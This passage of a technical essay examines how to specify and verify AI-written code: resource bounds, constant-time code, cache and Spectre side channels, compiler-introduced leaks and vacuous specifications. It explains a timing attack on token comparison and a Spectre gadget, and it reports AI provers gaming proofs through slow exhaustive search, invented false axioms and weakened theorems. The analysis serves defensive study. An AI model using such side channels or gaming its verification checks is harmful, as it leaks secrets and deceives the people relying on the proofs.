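Only the last specification catches the problem. A limit on average cost doesn't protect against an attacker who chooses the input. Polynomial potential would not help much either. No linear polynomial stays above n log₂ n, so the best bound this method can give any sorting routine with that cost is quadratic, and this quicksort satisfies a quadratic limit.

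Merge sort, which repeatedly merges short sorted lists into longer ones, meets the last specification. *CSLib* includes a proof that merge sort needs at most n⌈log₂ n⌉ comparisons, which is 1.7 million here. Another remedy is to choose quicksort's pivots at random. The expected number of comparisons is then low for every input, including sorted ones, provided the attacker cannot predict the choices.

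A meter set to 20 million steps would also stop the attack after about 20 milliseconds. But sorted lists are common, and an honest customer who submitted one would get no result.

### Verified programs that are far too slow

AI agents have written verified code as wasteful as the payroll function that tries every possible order of the records. In *Vero*, Ye, Lou and colleagues (2026) asked agents to implement 43 software repositories in Lean and prove them correct. One repository uses the Hungarian algorithm, an efficient way to assign workers to jobs at the lowest total cost. Three of the four agent configurations replaced it with a program that lists every possible assignment and picks the cheapest.

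The agents had a good reason to do this, even without bad intent, because the specifications didn't limit resource use and the slow program is much easier to prove correct. When they had to use the efficient version, every configuration proved exactly 12 of the 19 specifications. With the exhaustive search, these three proved all 19. In another repository, an agent replaced binary search with a scan of the whole list and proved all 49 specifications, compared with 24 for the original code.

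More complete functional specifications do not solve this. *Djinnlang* (Henniger, Chong and Amin, 2026) requires a specification to allow exactly one output for each input, which closes leaks such as the one through the payroll function's half-cent rounding allowance. Claude Fable 5.1 and GPT-6 Astra each proved all 256 obligations for three programs. But on hard Sudoku puzzles, GPT-6's solver had not finished after 15 minutes. After both models had a chance to optimize, it took 47.84 seconds and Claude's took 0.13. Henniger and colleagues warn that a model could deliberately write code that is slow on some inputs, and they plan to add bounds on resource use to the language.

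Another option is to ask a model to look for slow code. *AuXSpec* (2026) instructs an AI auditor to flag an implementation if it takes more than about 10⁷ steps on the largest permitted input and the best known method is faster by more than a logarithmic factor. The quicksort above would meet both conditions. This review rule is sensible, but it relies on the auditor's judgment rather than a proof.

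Proofs of cost bounds for model-written code are still uncommon. Lehre (2026), in *Agentic Algorithm Design*, had Claude models invent search algorithms and prove in Lean how long they take on average in the worst case. Each algorithm looks for the best string of bits by asking for the scores of strings it chooses, and its cost is the number of questions. Of 15 runs, 12 ended with a proved bound:

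- Nine gave a polynomial bound for an algorithm whose other computation is spelled out. One solves a new problem in O(n²) questions, while a standard evolutionary algorithm needs exponentially many.
- Two gave a polynomial bound by exploiting the cost model. The problem was to find a smallest vertex cover, for which nobody knows an efficient general method. The algorithms asked enough questions to learn the whole problem, then solved it between questions, where computation was free.
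- One improved on random guessing only by a constant factor.

The bounds were often loose. For one algorithm whose resource use is O(n log n), the model proved a bound of O(n³). A loose bound is still correct, but it may be too weak to rule out an attack.

### Mining within the budget

Cryptocurrency mining means computing huge numbers of hashes in search of one that earns a reward. Suppose a payroll program is allowed 20 million steps per run but needs only 4 million. A hostile author can use the other 16 million for mining, and the program will still meet its functional specification and stay within its step limit.

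Counting a program's steps doesn't show whether those steps serve its task. A program that stores passwords safely computes many hashes, as a cryptocurrency miner does, and the two may use the same instructions. The owner can lower the limit, but a worst-case limit has to allow for the input that needs the most steps. Insertion sort needs about 5 billion comparisons for 100,000 records in descending order but only 99,999 if they are already sorted, so on a sorted list the program could use nearly all of its allowed steps for something else.

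The other kinds of specification can make mining pointless, though. A miner has to report a winning hash to somebody, and a program has no ordinary way to report one if it has no network capability and its specification fixes every digit of the output. It can still waste electricity, and it might signal the result through its running time.

### Comparing with a reference program

A relational cost specification can leave less room for misuse. It compares the new program with a trusted one on the same input:

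for every input x, cost(new, x) ≤ c × cost(reference, x)

With c = 1.1, the program can use at most 10% more resources than the reference on any input, so it no longer has a large unused allowance on inputs that need few resources. The same rule would have excluded the exhaustive search in *Vero*, where every function came with a reference implementation. But Ye and colleagues point out that the original repositories provide no cost model, and without one, resource use is undefined.

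*Relational Cost Analysis for Functional-Imperative Programs* (Qu, Gaboardi and Garg, 2018) presents a type system that bounds the difference in resource use between two programs, or between two runs of one program on different inputs. To limit a program to c times the resource use of a reference program, the owner can multiply all the reference program's weights by c and require that the program's total never exceed the reference program's.

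Such proofs work best when the programs have a similar structure, because most of the steps then cancel. *Bidirectional Type Checking for Relational Properties* (2018) gives the example of applying a function to every element of two lists that differ in at most α places. If the function's resource use varies by at most t, the totals differ by at most t × α, however long the lists are. When the programs are too different, *A Relational Logic for Higher-Order Programs* (2017) describes a fallback, which is to subtract the reference's minimum resource use from the new program's maximum. This requires a lower bound on the reference, which most resource analyses do not provide. *Two-Sided Amortized Resource Analysis* (2026) verifies lower bounds as well as upper bounds.

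Even with perfect proofs, the choice of reference remains a problem. If the reference is the quicksort above, the rule allows the new program to take 10 billion steps on a sorted list too. If the reference is insertion sort, the rule can reject a better program. On a sorted list of 100,000 records, insertion sort makes 99,999 comparisons and merge sort makes more than 800,000. Merge sort therefore fails for c = 2, although it is thousands of times faster in the worst case. Adding a fixed allowance for each record would let merge sort pass, but it would also give a miner more steps to use.

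## Constant-time code and what hardware leaks

A program can stay within its resource limit on every input and still leak a secret, if the amount it uses depends on that secret. Suppose a website gives each user a token of 16 random bytes, and this function compares the real token with the one that a visitor submits:

```
def check(token, guess):
    for i in range(16):
        if token[i] != guess[i]:
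            return False
    return True
```

The function is correct, because it returns True exactly when the tokens match. An attacker guessing blindly would have to search 256¹⁶ tokens, or about 3.4 × 10³⁸. But the function stops at the first mismatch, so a guess with the right first byte takes slightly longer than one with a wrong first byte. The attacker can try all 256 values of the first byte, keep the slowest, and then do the same for each later byte. This takes at most 16 × 256 = 4,096 guesses. Real measurements are noisy, but even if the attacker has to repeat each guess 10,000 times, the total is only about 41 million.

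The usual remedy is to compare every byte, even after a mismatch:

```
def check_ct(token, guess):
    diff = 0
    for i in range(16):
        diff |= token[i] ^ guess[i]
    return diff == 0
```

`^` gives 0 only when two bytes are equal, and `|=` records any difference in `diff`, so `diff` is 0 at the end only if all 16 bytes match. The two functions return the same result for every input, so they satisfy exactly the same specifications of functional correctness.

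### What an attacker can observe

Cryptographers specify constant-time code using a leakage model, a formal list of what they assume an attacker can observe besides outputs. The usual model includes which way each branch goes and the address of every memory access, because these cause timing differences. They use this model rather than a limit in nanoseconds because the running time depends on the processor, its temperature and whatever else is running.

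Addresses matter because a processor keeps recently used memory in a small, fast store called a cache. An attacker who runs a program on the same machine can fill the cache with their own data, wait for the victim's program to run, and then time how long it takes to read that data again. The slow reads show which parts of the cache the victim used, and therefore roughly which addresses. Stricter models also record the operands of instructions, such as division, that take longer for some numbers than others.

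Write leak(p, m) for the list of observations when program p starts in memory m. The program is constant-time if the following holds for all memories m₁ and m₂:

if m₁ =L m₂, then leak(p, m₁) = leak(p, m₂)

This is noninterference with the observations in place of the public output. Suppose the guess starts with the byte 7, one token starts with 7 and another starts with 9. `check` goes on to the next byte with the first token but returns with the second. The two lists of observations therefore differ, so the function is not constant-time. `check_ct` reads positions 0 to 15 in order whatever the token contains.

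The definition also rules out leaks through termination. The program that counts upwards and loops forever when it reaches the director's salary passes an ordinary information-flow type checker, but it is not constant-time because it branches on the salary.

The name "constant-time" is misleading because the running time can vary. A constant-time program may take longer for a long message than for a short one if the length is public, and it may also take longer when its data is not in the cache.

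The result of `check_ct` still depends on the token, and the website has to branch on that result to decide whether to let the visitor in. A specification for the whole login page therefore needs a release policy. The policy can require equal observations only for pairs of memories in which `check_ct` returns the same result for the guess, as delimited release does for outputs. The page may then reveal whether a guess was right, but not how many of its bytes matched.

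### Proving that two runs look alike

Constant-time compares two runs, so self-composition applies, and the comparison is easier than for secrecy in general. Two runs of a constant-time program take every branch together, so a checker can combine them into a single program that runs both copies in step. José Bacelar Almeida and colleagues used such product programs in ct-verif, a checker from 2016. Before each branch, the product program asserts that both copies are about to go the same way, and before each memory access it asserts that both use the same address. Leaving out the assertions that obviously hold, the product program for `check` is:

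```
assume guess1 == guess2
for i in range(16):
    assert (token1[i] != guess1[i]) == (token2[i] != guess2[i])
    if token1[i] != guess1[i]:
        return
```

The assertion fails on the first pass if only one of the tokens starts with the same byte as the guess. The product program for `check_ct` has no such assertion, because its only branch is the loop test and the addresses it accesses depend on i.

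ct-verif works on the intermediate code of LLVM, a compiler framework that many languages share. LLVM translates source code into this intermediate code, improves it, and then translates it into machine code for a particular processor.

Zhang and Barthe's *CT-LLVM* uses a simpler method, taint analysis. The tool follows each secret through every computation that uses it and reports any secret that reaches a branch condition, a memory address or an instruction with variable timing. Unlike a general information-flow checker, it can ignore implicit flows, because a program that branches on a secret has already failed the check.

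In nine cryptographic libraries, the tool could soundly analyze 36% of the functions on average, and it proved 61% of those constant-time. It skips functions that use function pointers, contain hand-written assembly or call code it has no access to. The tool treats every argument as a possible secret and leaves a person to decide which ones are, so a function that fails is not necessarily faulty. This approach makes it practical to check a whole library, including parts that experts overlook. One such part is the code that decodes Base64, a text format in which libraries store private keys. Most of the libraries decoded it by looking up each character in a table, and nobody ran a constant-time checker on that code until 2021.

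Taint analysis can raise false alarms, and self-composition, which compares two full runs of a program, is slow on large programs. *Towards Efficient Verification of Constant-Time Cryptographic Implementations* (2024) combines them, using taint analysis to rule out most of the suspected leaks and self-composition to check the rest.

Binsec/Rel checks machine code directly, using relational symbolic execution. It runs a program on symbols instead of numbers, so one symbolic run represents many real ones. It tracks two runs together, with the same public inputs but different secrets, and at each branch or memory access it uses a solver to check whether any two secrets could lead to different observations. If the solver finds such a pair, it returns the two secrets. Otherwise, the code is proved constant-time only up to a fixed number of instructions, which for cryptography often corresponds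 to a particular key size.

In Jasmin, a language for cryptography, the programmer labels data as public or secret, and a type checker rejects any branch or memory address that depends on a secret. A separate machine-checked proof shows that the Jasmin compiler preserves the constant-time property.

### Testing compiled code

*DALC-CT* (Njungle, Kayang and colleagues, 2026) describes a tool that tests compiled programs rather than proving properties of them. It runs a function on several secrets, counts the executed instructions in each of 13 categories, and reports a violation if any count differs between runs. In the paper's example, the password is "secret" and the input is either "secret" or "secure". A comparison that stops at the first mismatch executed 242 load instructions for the first input and 153 for the second. The constant-time version executed 259 for both. The tool gave the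 expected answer on all 22 test programs and never needed more than five runs to find a violation.

This is a good way to catch careless mistakes, but a much weaker check on a hostile author, who could write a function that behaves differently for only one token in a trillion. A handful of random runs will almost certainly miss that. Counting instructions also can't detect a table lookup at a secret address, because the processor executes the same instructions wherever it reads. Njungle and colleagues acknowledge that their method does not cover caches, and suggest combining it with measurements of real running times.

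The US standards agency NIST is choosing new digital signature schemes that should resist quantum computers, and it requires resistance to timing attacks. *Systematic Timing Leakage Analysis of NIST PQDSS Candidates* (Adjonyo, Bardin and colleagues, 2025) analyzes 302 versions of 15 candidate schemes. It uses Binsec/Rel2, the current version of Binsec/Rel, and TIMECOP, which runs the program once and tracks the secret key through memory. For some candidates it also uses two statistical tools, dudect and RTLF, which measure running times.

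TIMECOP raised alarms on every scheme it ran on. In a small sample that the researchers checked by hand, 67% of TIMECOP's alarms were false, while all of Binsec/Rel2's were real violations. One reason for the false alarms is that many schemes store public data in the same block of memory as the private key, and TIMECOP treated the whole block as secret.

Binsec/Rel2 was more precise, but every analysis ran out of memory or hit its 30-minute limit. The researchers had also set it up to find bugs quickly, treating only one byte of the key as secret, so the absence of an alarm did not prove the code free of leaks. Bounded proofs are possible in principle, but this set-up could not produce them for these schemes.

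The researchers reported 26 issues to the developers, who fixed five, acknowledged ten more but had not yet fixed them, rejected nine, and did not respond to two. One of the fixed issues was in Preon, which looked up values in a 256-byte table at a position that depended on the secret key. Caches usually load memory in 64-byte blocks, so a table of this size fills about four blocks. An attacker who sees which block the program used learns about two of the position's eight bits. Another fixed issue was in LESS, which shuffled a list by swapping entries at secret positions.

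Some violations of the constant-time property are harmless. Many cryptographic schemes draw random values until one has the right form and discard the others. The number of attempts depends on secret data, so the loop is not constant-time, but it usually reveals information only about values the scheme never uses. Like noninterference, the constant-time property is stricter than the protection people want, and each exception needs its own justification.

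Statistical tools can't show where a leak is or prove that none exists, but they need no leakage model, so they can catch leaks that such models omit. Adjonyo and colleagues recommend them as a last line of defense.

### How compilers undo the property

Programmers often avoid a branch by using arithmetic. Kyber, an encryption scheme that NIST has already selected, turns each bit of a secret message into either 0 or 1665. The code for this is roughly:

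```
mask = -bit                # all zeros if bit is 0, all ones if bit is 1
coefficient = mask & 1665  # 0 or 1665
```

There is no branch, so a source-level checker accepts it. *[RFC] Constant-Time Coding Support*, a proposal to the developers of LLVM, reproduces a case that Antoon Purnal documented in 2024. LLVM's C compiler, Clang, worked out that the result is always one of two constants, and produced machine code that does this:

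```
if bit == 0:
    coefficient = 0
else:
    coefficient = 1665
```

The machine code computes the same result but branches on a secret bit. This happened on x86-64, the usual processor type in PCs and servers, at a low optimization setting. It is not a compiler bug under the rules of C, which cover what a program computes but not how long it takes.

In *Breaking Bad*, Schneider, Lain and colleagues (2024) looked for leaks that compilers introduce. They compiled eight widely used cryptographic libraries with many versions of LLVM and GCC, another common compiler, for six types of processor and at seven optimization settings. They then ran each cryptographic function in an emulator with different secret keys and compared the branches taken and the memory addresses accessed. After they filtered out leaks that were already in the source code, 429 of the 5,716 programs that compiled had at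 least one branch that depended on a secret, and 368 had at least one memory access that did.

Five of the eight libraries were affected, including HACL\*, whose source code had a formal proof that it was free of such leaks. The proof was correct, but it relied on the compiler not to introduce any. A function in HACL\* uses a mask to choose between two values, x and y, depending on a secret. LLVM first replaced the mask with a `select` instruction in its intermediate code. For two types of processor, it then turned `select` into a branch. For two others, it produced code that uses the secret to calculate the address of x or y and reads only that value, which leaks the secret through the cache.

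These problems were more common on less popular processors, probably because developers check the popular ones more carefully. But LLVM compiled a BearSSL function to the same kind of secret-dependent read even on x86-64 and 64-bit Arm. Turning optimization off reduced the number of leaks but didn't remove them all. GCC compiled the carry in one library's 128-bit addition to a branch at every optimization level, including with optimization off.

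### Compilers that preserve it

One response is to prove that the compiler preserves the constant-time property as well as correctness. The proof must show that if two runs of the source program produce the same observations, the corresponding runs of the machine code do too. Researchers have done this for Jasmin and for a version of CompCert, the verified C compiler. *Fun with flags* (2025) notes that common libraries and software distributions use neither. Developers would have to rewrite large parts of their libraries to use Jasmin, and CompCert can be hard to fit into an existing build system.

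Another approach is to add an operation that an ordinary compiler must preserve. Trail of Bits' *Introducing constant-time support for LLVM to protect cryptographic code* (2025) presents `__builtin_ct_select`, which uses a condition to choose between two values without branching. On x86-64 it compiles to a conditional move, an instruction that takes the same time whichever value it selects. On processors without a suitable instruction, it compiles to bitwise arithmetic. In early tests at ETH Zurich, the operation remained constant-time at every optimization setting.

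Getting the constant-time selection operation into LLVM has been slow. In November 2025, Friedman (2025), in *[clang] [ConstantTime][Clang] Add __builtin_ct_select for constant-time selection (PR #166703)*, was still "generally skeptical of this approach" during the public code review. The review was still going on in May 2026, when Arsenault (2026) commented on the tests in the same thread. The LLVM 23.1.0 release notes do not list the operation among the changes to the intermediate code.

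Until compilers offer such guarantees, a checker can reject any code that might compile into a leak. Zhang and Barthe found that all the known leaks LLVM introduces involve its `select` instruction, so their tool can reject any `select` whose condition is secret. This rejects some code that would have compiled safely, and it would not catch a new optimization that leaks in another way. The most direct approach is to check the machine code, as Binsec/Rel does, but someone then has to repeat the check for each processor and compiler version.

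For AI-generated code, this means the compiled program is the thing to accept or reject. An owner who checks the source code and then compiles it with an ordinary compiler has evidence about a slightly different program from the one that runs.

### What the processor does on its own

Even machine code with a correct proof can leak, because processors do things that the leakage model leaves out. The most important is speculative execution. A processor that has to wait for data before it can decide a branch will guess the outcome and carry on. If the guess was wrong, it discards the results. The attack called Spectre, which researchers published in 2018, exploits code like this:

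```
if i < n:
    x = a[i]
    y = table[64 * x]
```

Here `a` has n entries, and the attacker chooses i. After a series of valid values, the processor predicts that i will be less than n. The attacker then supplies a larger i that points to a secret byte beyond the end of the array. While waiting for n, the processor reads the secret into x and uses it to choose a position in `table`. When n arrives and the check fails, the processor discards x and y, but the block it read from `table` stays in the cache. Each value of x selects a different 64-byte block, so an attacker who finds out which block is cached learns the secret.

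In the usual leakage model, this program never reads outside the array, because the branch skips both reads when the index is out of bounds. The proof is valid, but the model doesn't include what the processor executes after it mispredicts a branch.

One defense, speculative load hardening, makes the program track whether it is on a wrongly guessed path and, if so, blank out what it loads. Protecting every load slows the program, so *VellSSLH* (2026) uses types to work out which loads need protection. The method is meant to miss none that matter, and the paper tests it on 24 cryptographic operations from sources such as libsodium, HACL\* and Kyber.

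Some processors also use the contents of memory to predict which data a program will need next. If a value looks like an address, a data-dependent prefetcher may load whatever is at that address, even if the program never uses the value as one. In 2024, researchers used this behavior to recover secret keys from constant-time programs on Apple's M1 chip, in an attack called GoFetch. The attacker chose inputs so that an intermediate value looked like an address only if a guess about the key was right, then checked the cache to see whether the prefetcher had loaded data from that address.

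Frequency scaling can leak information about a secret through running time, even when the secret affects neither branches nor addresses. Processors slow down to avoid overheating, and the heat they produce depends partly on the numbers they handle. As Adjonyo and colleagues explain, operands with more 1 bits can change the temperature enough to change the processor's speed, so an attacker who measures the running time can learn roughly how many 1 bits a secret has.

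Carelessly written code is unlikely to leak much this way, but a hostile author could look for operations whose heat or prefetching depends strongly on a secret and use them repeatedly, without invalidating the proof that the code is constant-time.

### Contracts for processors

Programmers can't examine a processor's design for every function they write, and the details are often trade secrets. A hardware-software contract solves this problem by stating what a processor may reveal about any program. *Coverage-Guided Pre-Silicon Fuzzing of Open-Source Processors based on Leakage Contracts* (Geier, Hajipour and Reineke, 2025) formally defines a contract, which attaches observations to each instruction. C(p, s) is the list of these observations when program p starts in state s, which contains the memory and registers that a program can use.

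The processor also has a hidden state h, which includes the contents of its cache and its record of past branches. Write A(p, s, h) for what an attacker sees on the real hardware, such as the number of clock cycles. The processor satisfies the contract if the following holds for every program p, every hidden state h and all states s₁ and s₂:

if C(p, s₁) = C(p, s₂), then A(p, s₁, h) = A(p, s₂, h)

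The attacker learns only what the contract allows from the hardware. Software developers prove that C(p, s) does not depend on secrets, which is the constant-time property with the contract as the leakage model. Hardware designers prove that their processor satisfies the contract. Together, the two proofs show that A(p, s, h) does not depend on secrets.

Geier and colleagues use two main contracts. The first, seq-ct, lets the processor reveal which instructions run and the address of each load and store, as in ordinary constant-time programming. The second, seq-arch, also lets it reveal every value that the program loads. Seq-arch therefore can't protect a key that the program itself reads, but it helps when running untrusted code in a sandbox. If the sandbox never lets the code load a secret, a processor that satisfies seq-arch can't reveal one through speculation. An owner who denies an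 AI-generated program access to the salaries depends on such a guarantee as well as on the programming language or the sandbox.

Small details of a contract matter. The first version of seq-ct recorded only which instruction ran next. In rare cases a branch leads to the same instruction whether or not the program takes it, so the contract doesn't reveal the outcome, although the timing might. Geier and colleagues therefore added a stricter variant that records each branch's outcome.

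Proving that a processor satisfies a contract is possible for small designs but impractical for industrial ones. Geier and colleagues instead test processors by simulating two copies side by side, with both running the same random program on different data. If the contract's observations match but the two copies finish at different times, the processor violates the contract. To search efficiently, they favor test programs that make the internal states of the two copies differ in new ways.

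The researchers tested this on two open-source processors. Rocket, which runs instructions in order, probably satisfies the stricter version of seq-ct. BOOM, which runs instructions speculatively, is known to violate both seq-ct and seq-arch, and the guided search found violations faster than an unguided one. The researchers left out multiplication and division because the timing of multiplication depends on the operands, which would have produced violations almost immediately. Code that multiplies secrets on such a processor would need a contract that reveals the operands, and it would then fail the check.

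Manufacturers informally document part of what their hardware leaks. Arm and Intel list instructions whose timing does not depend on their operands, though in some cases this holds only after software turns on a special mode. A full contract for a commercial processor would also have to cover speculation, prefetching and frequency scaling, and outsiders could not verify that the processor meets it without access to the design.

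### What AI-assisted verification covers

AI has made verifying cryptographic code much faster, but the largest projects stop at functional correctness. *Scaling Verification of Cryptographic Software with Aeneas, Rust, and Lean* (Ho, Fournet and colleagues, 2026) describes verification work on SymCrypt, the main cryptographic library in Windows. AI agents wrote most of the proofs, and Lean checked them. The resulting 237,000 lines of Lean show that 16,700 lines of Rust, a language designed for memory safety, implement the published standards and never stop with a run-time error. Verifying one part of one algorithm originally took about six months. An agent now needs about a week, plus a few days of human review, to formalize, write and verify a whole new algorithm.

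The programmers wrote the Rust code in a constant-time style, but the proofs do not cover leakage. This is probably mainly because the tool Aeneas translates the code into mathematical functions in Lean that have no pointers or memory. The translation makes it far easier to prove what the code computes, but it removes the addresses needed to define constant-time execution. Two versions of a function that compute the same value but read different addresses could become almost the same formula.

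Microsoft relies on testing for leakage, using fuzzing and symbolic execution on the compiled code, so the tests also catch leaks that the compiler introduces. But Ho and colleagues describe this protection as informal and mention it only for x86-64, while the correctness proofs also cover Arm.

In *An AI Approach to Verified Production Cryptographic Libraries*, Sun, Fong and colleagues (2026) verified curve25519-dalek, a Rust library that the messaging app Signal uses. People supplied the specifications of the public functions and a library of trusted facts, and Claude wrote everything in between in 11.4 hours for $466.99. The original developers had needed three people and five months to verify the same library, though they also had to write the specifications. The system then verified an implementation of the ChaCha20 cipher in 15 minutes for $4.14.

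As Sun and colleagues state, these proofs don't cover timing either. The system does not change the executable code, so the libraries are as resistant to timing attacks as before. If `check` had been one of the functions, the system could have proved it correct despite the timing problem.

An earlier version of the system reported finishing 97.1% of the work, but an audit found that 11 of its proofs relied on axioms it had invented, ten of which were false. The prompt prohibited new axioms, but no program enforced that rule. The rule against changing the specification was enforced by a program and was never broken. Sun and colleagues then added automatic checks for invented axioms and for proofs that break other modules. A system that proved code constant-time would need the same protection for its labels and leakage model, since an agent could make any program pass by labeling the key as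 public.

In *An Empirical Security Evaluation of LLM-Generated Cryptographic Rust Code*, Elsayed, Fulton and Yang (2026) asked three models, all now old, for 240 programs that encrypt and decrypt data, and only 56 compiled. An analyzer with nine rules checked for mistakes such as keys written into the source code, weak random numbers and reuse of a nonce, a number that a program must use only once with each key. It found one key in the source code, one reused nonce and 32 programs with careless error handling.

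None of the nine rules concerns timing. This omission is less serious because the programs called existing encryption libraries, which do most of the secret-dependent work. Timing matters more when the model itself writes the cipher or a comparison such as `check`.

None of the three projects examined whether AI-written code or proofs protect against timing attacks. There is no obvious technical barrier to doing so. Constant-time is precisely defined and checkers for it exist, so a model could write a function in Jasmin, or revise its code until CT-LLVM accepts it. Proving whole libraries constant-time would be a natural next task for the agents that wrote the correctness proofs.

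### The cost of constant-time outside cryptography

Constant-time works well as a specification for cryptography because everyone agrees on what is secret (the key, but not its length). Most algorithms also perform a fixed series of arithmetic steps, so avoiding branches on the key takes little extra work. Even a small leak can be disastrous, because it may let an attacker recover the key and read every message it protects. Yet in a survey that Zhang and Barthe cite, developers of only 15 of 27 libraries used any constant-time checker. Most of those used the same one, which tests individual runs and so can't prove that code is constant-time.

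Ordinary software varies much more in how hard it is to protect. The payroll function `honest` would be easy. It uses the public departments to decide where to store each total, and it only adds the salaries. If the salaries are 64-bit integers, the additions take the same time whatever the amounts. The final division may take longer for some totals than for others, but anyone who knows the department's size can already calculate the total from the published average.

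A function that branches on salaries takes more computation. If tax depends on which of five bands a salary falls into, constant-time code has to calculate the tax for all five and select the right one with a mask. To look up one employee in a sorted list of 100,000 without revealing which one, the program has to read all 100,000 records, while binary search reads about 17. Sorting by salary requires a sequence of comparisons that doesn't depend on their results. Ken Batcher's standard method needs about 9 million comparisons for this list, padded to the next power of two, while merge sort needs at most 1.7 million.

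Compilers can do some of the rewriting. *Compiler Support for Constant-Time Programs in LLVM* describes a tool that tracks secrets through a program, finds the branches and addresses that depend on them, and replaces each such branch with code that executes both sides. This saves the programmer work, but the program still takes extra time to execute both sides. A loop whose length depends on a secret also has to run for its maximum length every time, so that maximum must be known. Many business programs use databases, text processing and automatic memory management, whose own code branches on the data it handles. Making a whole program constant-time would mean rewriting or replacing that code too.

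An easier option for most software is to control when results leave the machine. If the payroll service always finishes within a second and sends every reply exactly one second after it receives the request, a remote customer learns nothing from the delay. This needs only a limit on running time, which is a property of single runs and much easier to prove. The fixed delay doesn't protect against an attacker who shares the cache, so the owner also has to keep other people's programs off the machine while the service handles salaries. For a small function that handles keys or tokens, such as `check`, constant-time code adds a few instructions and is worth requiring from any author, human or AI.

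## Whether the specification says what was meant

Constant-time verification works for cryptography because people already agree on what to prove. Most software has no such agreement, so a sound proof can establish a property that nobody cares about.

### Proofs that establish almost nothing

In the verification language Dafny, a precondition starts with `requires` and a postcondition with `ensures`. Both are optional, so Dafny accepts this payroll method, which returns an empty table whatever the records contain:

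```
method Averages(records: seq<Record>) returns (result: map<Dept, real>)
{
  result := map[];
}
```

Dafny still checks that the method stops and that it never reads outside a list or divides by zero. The method passes, so anyone can truthfully call it verified.

Contradictory assumptions are harder to notice. Anything follows from a contradiction, so a verifier given contradictory assumptions can accept any program. Suppose a specification includes the assumptions that every hash has 256 bits and that no two files have the same hash. Programmers rely on both in practice, but there are only 2²⁵⁶ possible hashes and infinitely many files, so some files must share a hash. A prover could use this contradiction to prove that the payroll function returns the right averages, or that it returns the wrong ones. Testing wouldn't expose the problem, because nobody knows how to find two files that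 share a hash. Cryptographers avoid the contradiction by assuming that such pairs are hard to find, rather than that none exist.

One safeguard is to require an example that satisfies all the assumptions at once. The example is an input for a precondition, or a function for assumptions about an outside function. In the hash case, nobody could write such a function. This safeguard matters more with AI provers because they sometimes introduce false axioms, as one did while verifying the curve25519-dalek library.

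A postcondition can also be present but too weak. Vempaty, Sompalle and colleagues (2026), in *Verified but Vacuous*, describe a method that should return the largest number in a list. In Dafny, their example looks roughly like this:

```
predicate MaxCorrect(nums: seq<int>, r: int) { r >= 0 }

method Max(nums: seq<int>) returns (r: int)
  ensures MaxCorrect(nums, r)
{
  r := 0;
}
```

For the list 5, 3, 7, the method returns 0, and the proof is valid because 0 ≥ 0. A reviewer who reads only the last lines sees a method that "ensures MaxCorrect".

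Experts also write specifications that leave out part of what they meant. *The Specification Spectrum*, a post on Livshits's blog, recommends testing AI-generated code against general properties instead of individual examples. Its sample property for a sorting function requires each element of the result to be no larger than the next, so a function that always returns an empty list would pass. It should also require the result to contain the same elements as the input.

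If an AI system writes both the statement and the proof, it can replace a hard statement with an easier one. *AXLE* (2026), which describes online tools for Lean, notes that a file can compile while proving a weakened version of the intended theorem. Its strict checker reads the intended theorem from a separate file and accepts a proof only if the proved theorem matches it. This guarantees that the AI proved the owner's statement, but the owner could still have written something like `MaxCorrect`.

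### How often "verified" code has a useful specification

Vempaty and colleagues measured how common these problems are by applying three checks in order:

1. The verifier accepts the program.
2. At least one postcondition refers to a predicate or function defined in a separate specification file.
3. The specification captures what the user wanted. The researchers estimate this by running the verified program on hidden tests. They also use a method called Post2Exe, which turns the postcondition into a runnable program and tests whether it accepts right answers and rejects wrong ones.

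Their first experiment reproduced another group's system, in which a language model writes Dafny code and a compiler translates it into Python. With Claude Opus 4.7 as the model, they generated ten solutions to each problem in three sets of programming exercises. The last two columns of this table are shares of the programs that Dafny accepted:

| Exercises | Accepted by Dafny | Has any postcondition | Refers to a separate definition |
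|---|---|---|---|
| HumanEval | 99.1% | 5.3% | 1.9% |
| LeetCodeDataset | 97.2% | 9.6% | 2.7% |
| LiveCodeBench v6 | 92.2% | 10.6% | 2.3% |

The sample prompt, taken from the original system, probably explains much of this. Its example had no postcondition and listed the right answers in `expect` statements. Dafny checks an `expect` statement when the program runs but assumes it is true during verification, so the right answers entered the proof as assumptions. The code was mostly good, and 92.6% of the HumanEval solutions passed the basic tests, but the evidence for their correctness came from the tests rather than the proofs.

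The researchers caution that a program can fail the second check and still have a meaningful proof. For a function that doubles a number, `ensures r == 2 * x` is a complete specification, but it fails because it doesn't refer to a separate definition, while a separately defined predicate that is always true passes. The 1.9% is therefore not an estimate of how many proofs were meaningful. The 5.3% is a better guide, since the other 94.7% had no postcondition. A separate definition is still useful for untrusted code, because the owner can review it and prevent the code's author from editing it.

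In the second experiment, the researchers used their own system, VCG, which produces Rust code and requires every verified component to pass the second check. Hidden tests failed for 124 of the 1,080 fully verified solutions (11.48%) to a set of basic exercises and 229 of the 1,545 (14.82%) to a set of contest problems. Weak specifications are an obvious possible cause, but errors in the translation to Rust, the test software or the benchmark's own answers could also cause failures, and the researchers did not separate these causes.

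Another result suggests that weak or mistaken specifications are common. Of the contest solutions, 1,316 were fully verified and passed the tests, but only 535 of these (40.7%) also passed the benchmark's full evaluation, which covers the precondition, the postcondition, the code and the proof. The code and proofs had already passed, so most of the other 781 presumably had a faulty precondition or postcondition. Specifications for ordinary business software are probably harder to get right than those for these short exercises, which came with clear instructions.

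Owners can use the same idea to test whether a specification rules out harmful programs. A payroll specification that accepts "leaky" or "slow", for example, needs more conditions. An owner could keep a collection of such programs and check every new specification against it. This can't prove that a specification is adequate, but it catches known mistakes with little effort.

### Signal's security as theorems

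The Signal protocol encrypts messages in several popular apps, and researchers have studied its security goals for years. Chaudhuri, Ferraiuolo and colleagues (2026), in *AlphaProof Code*, describe how Google DeepMind's AI agents proved that libsignal, the protocol's reference implementation, meets several of them:

- **Handshake secrecy.** When two people start a conversation, nobody else learns the secret key that their phones agree on.
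- **Authentication.** If Alice's phone accepts a message as Bob's, Bob's phone sent it.
- **Forward secrecy.** Someone who steals a phone's current keys can't use them to read earlier messages.
- **Post-compromise security.** After such a theft, new messages become secret again once the phones have exchanged fresh keys that the thief has not seen.

These short descriptions leave out details that a theorem must include. A simple formal version of forward secrecy might require that an attacker who learns a message stole a key for it before the phones deleted that key. If someone shortened the condition to "the attacker stole a key at some point", an attacker who stole a phone's keys in June could read messages from January without violating the theorem. The theorem would be easier to prove and could still be called "forward secrecy", but it would no longer guarantee that protection.

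Chaudhuri and colleagues' agents produced about 6.5 million lines of Lean proof. The proofs depend on about 26,000 trusted lines, which contain the security specifications and a formal model of AArch64, the machine language of 64-bit Arm processors. Lean checks the proofs, so people need to review only the trusted lines.

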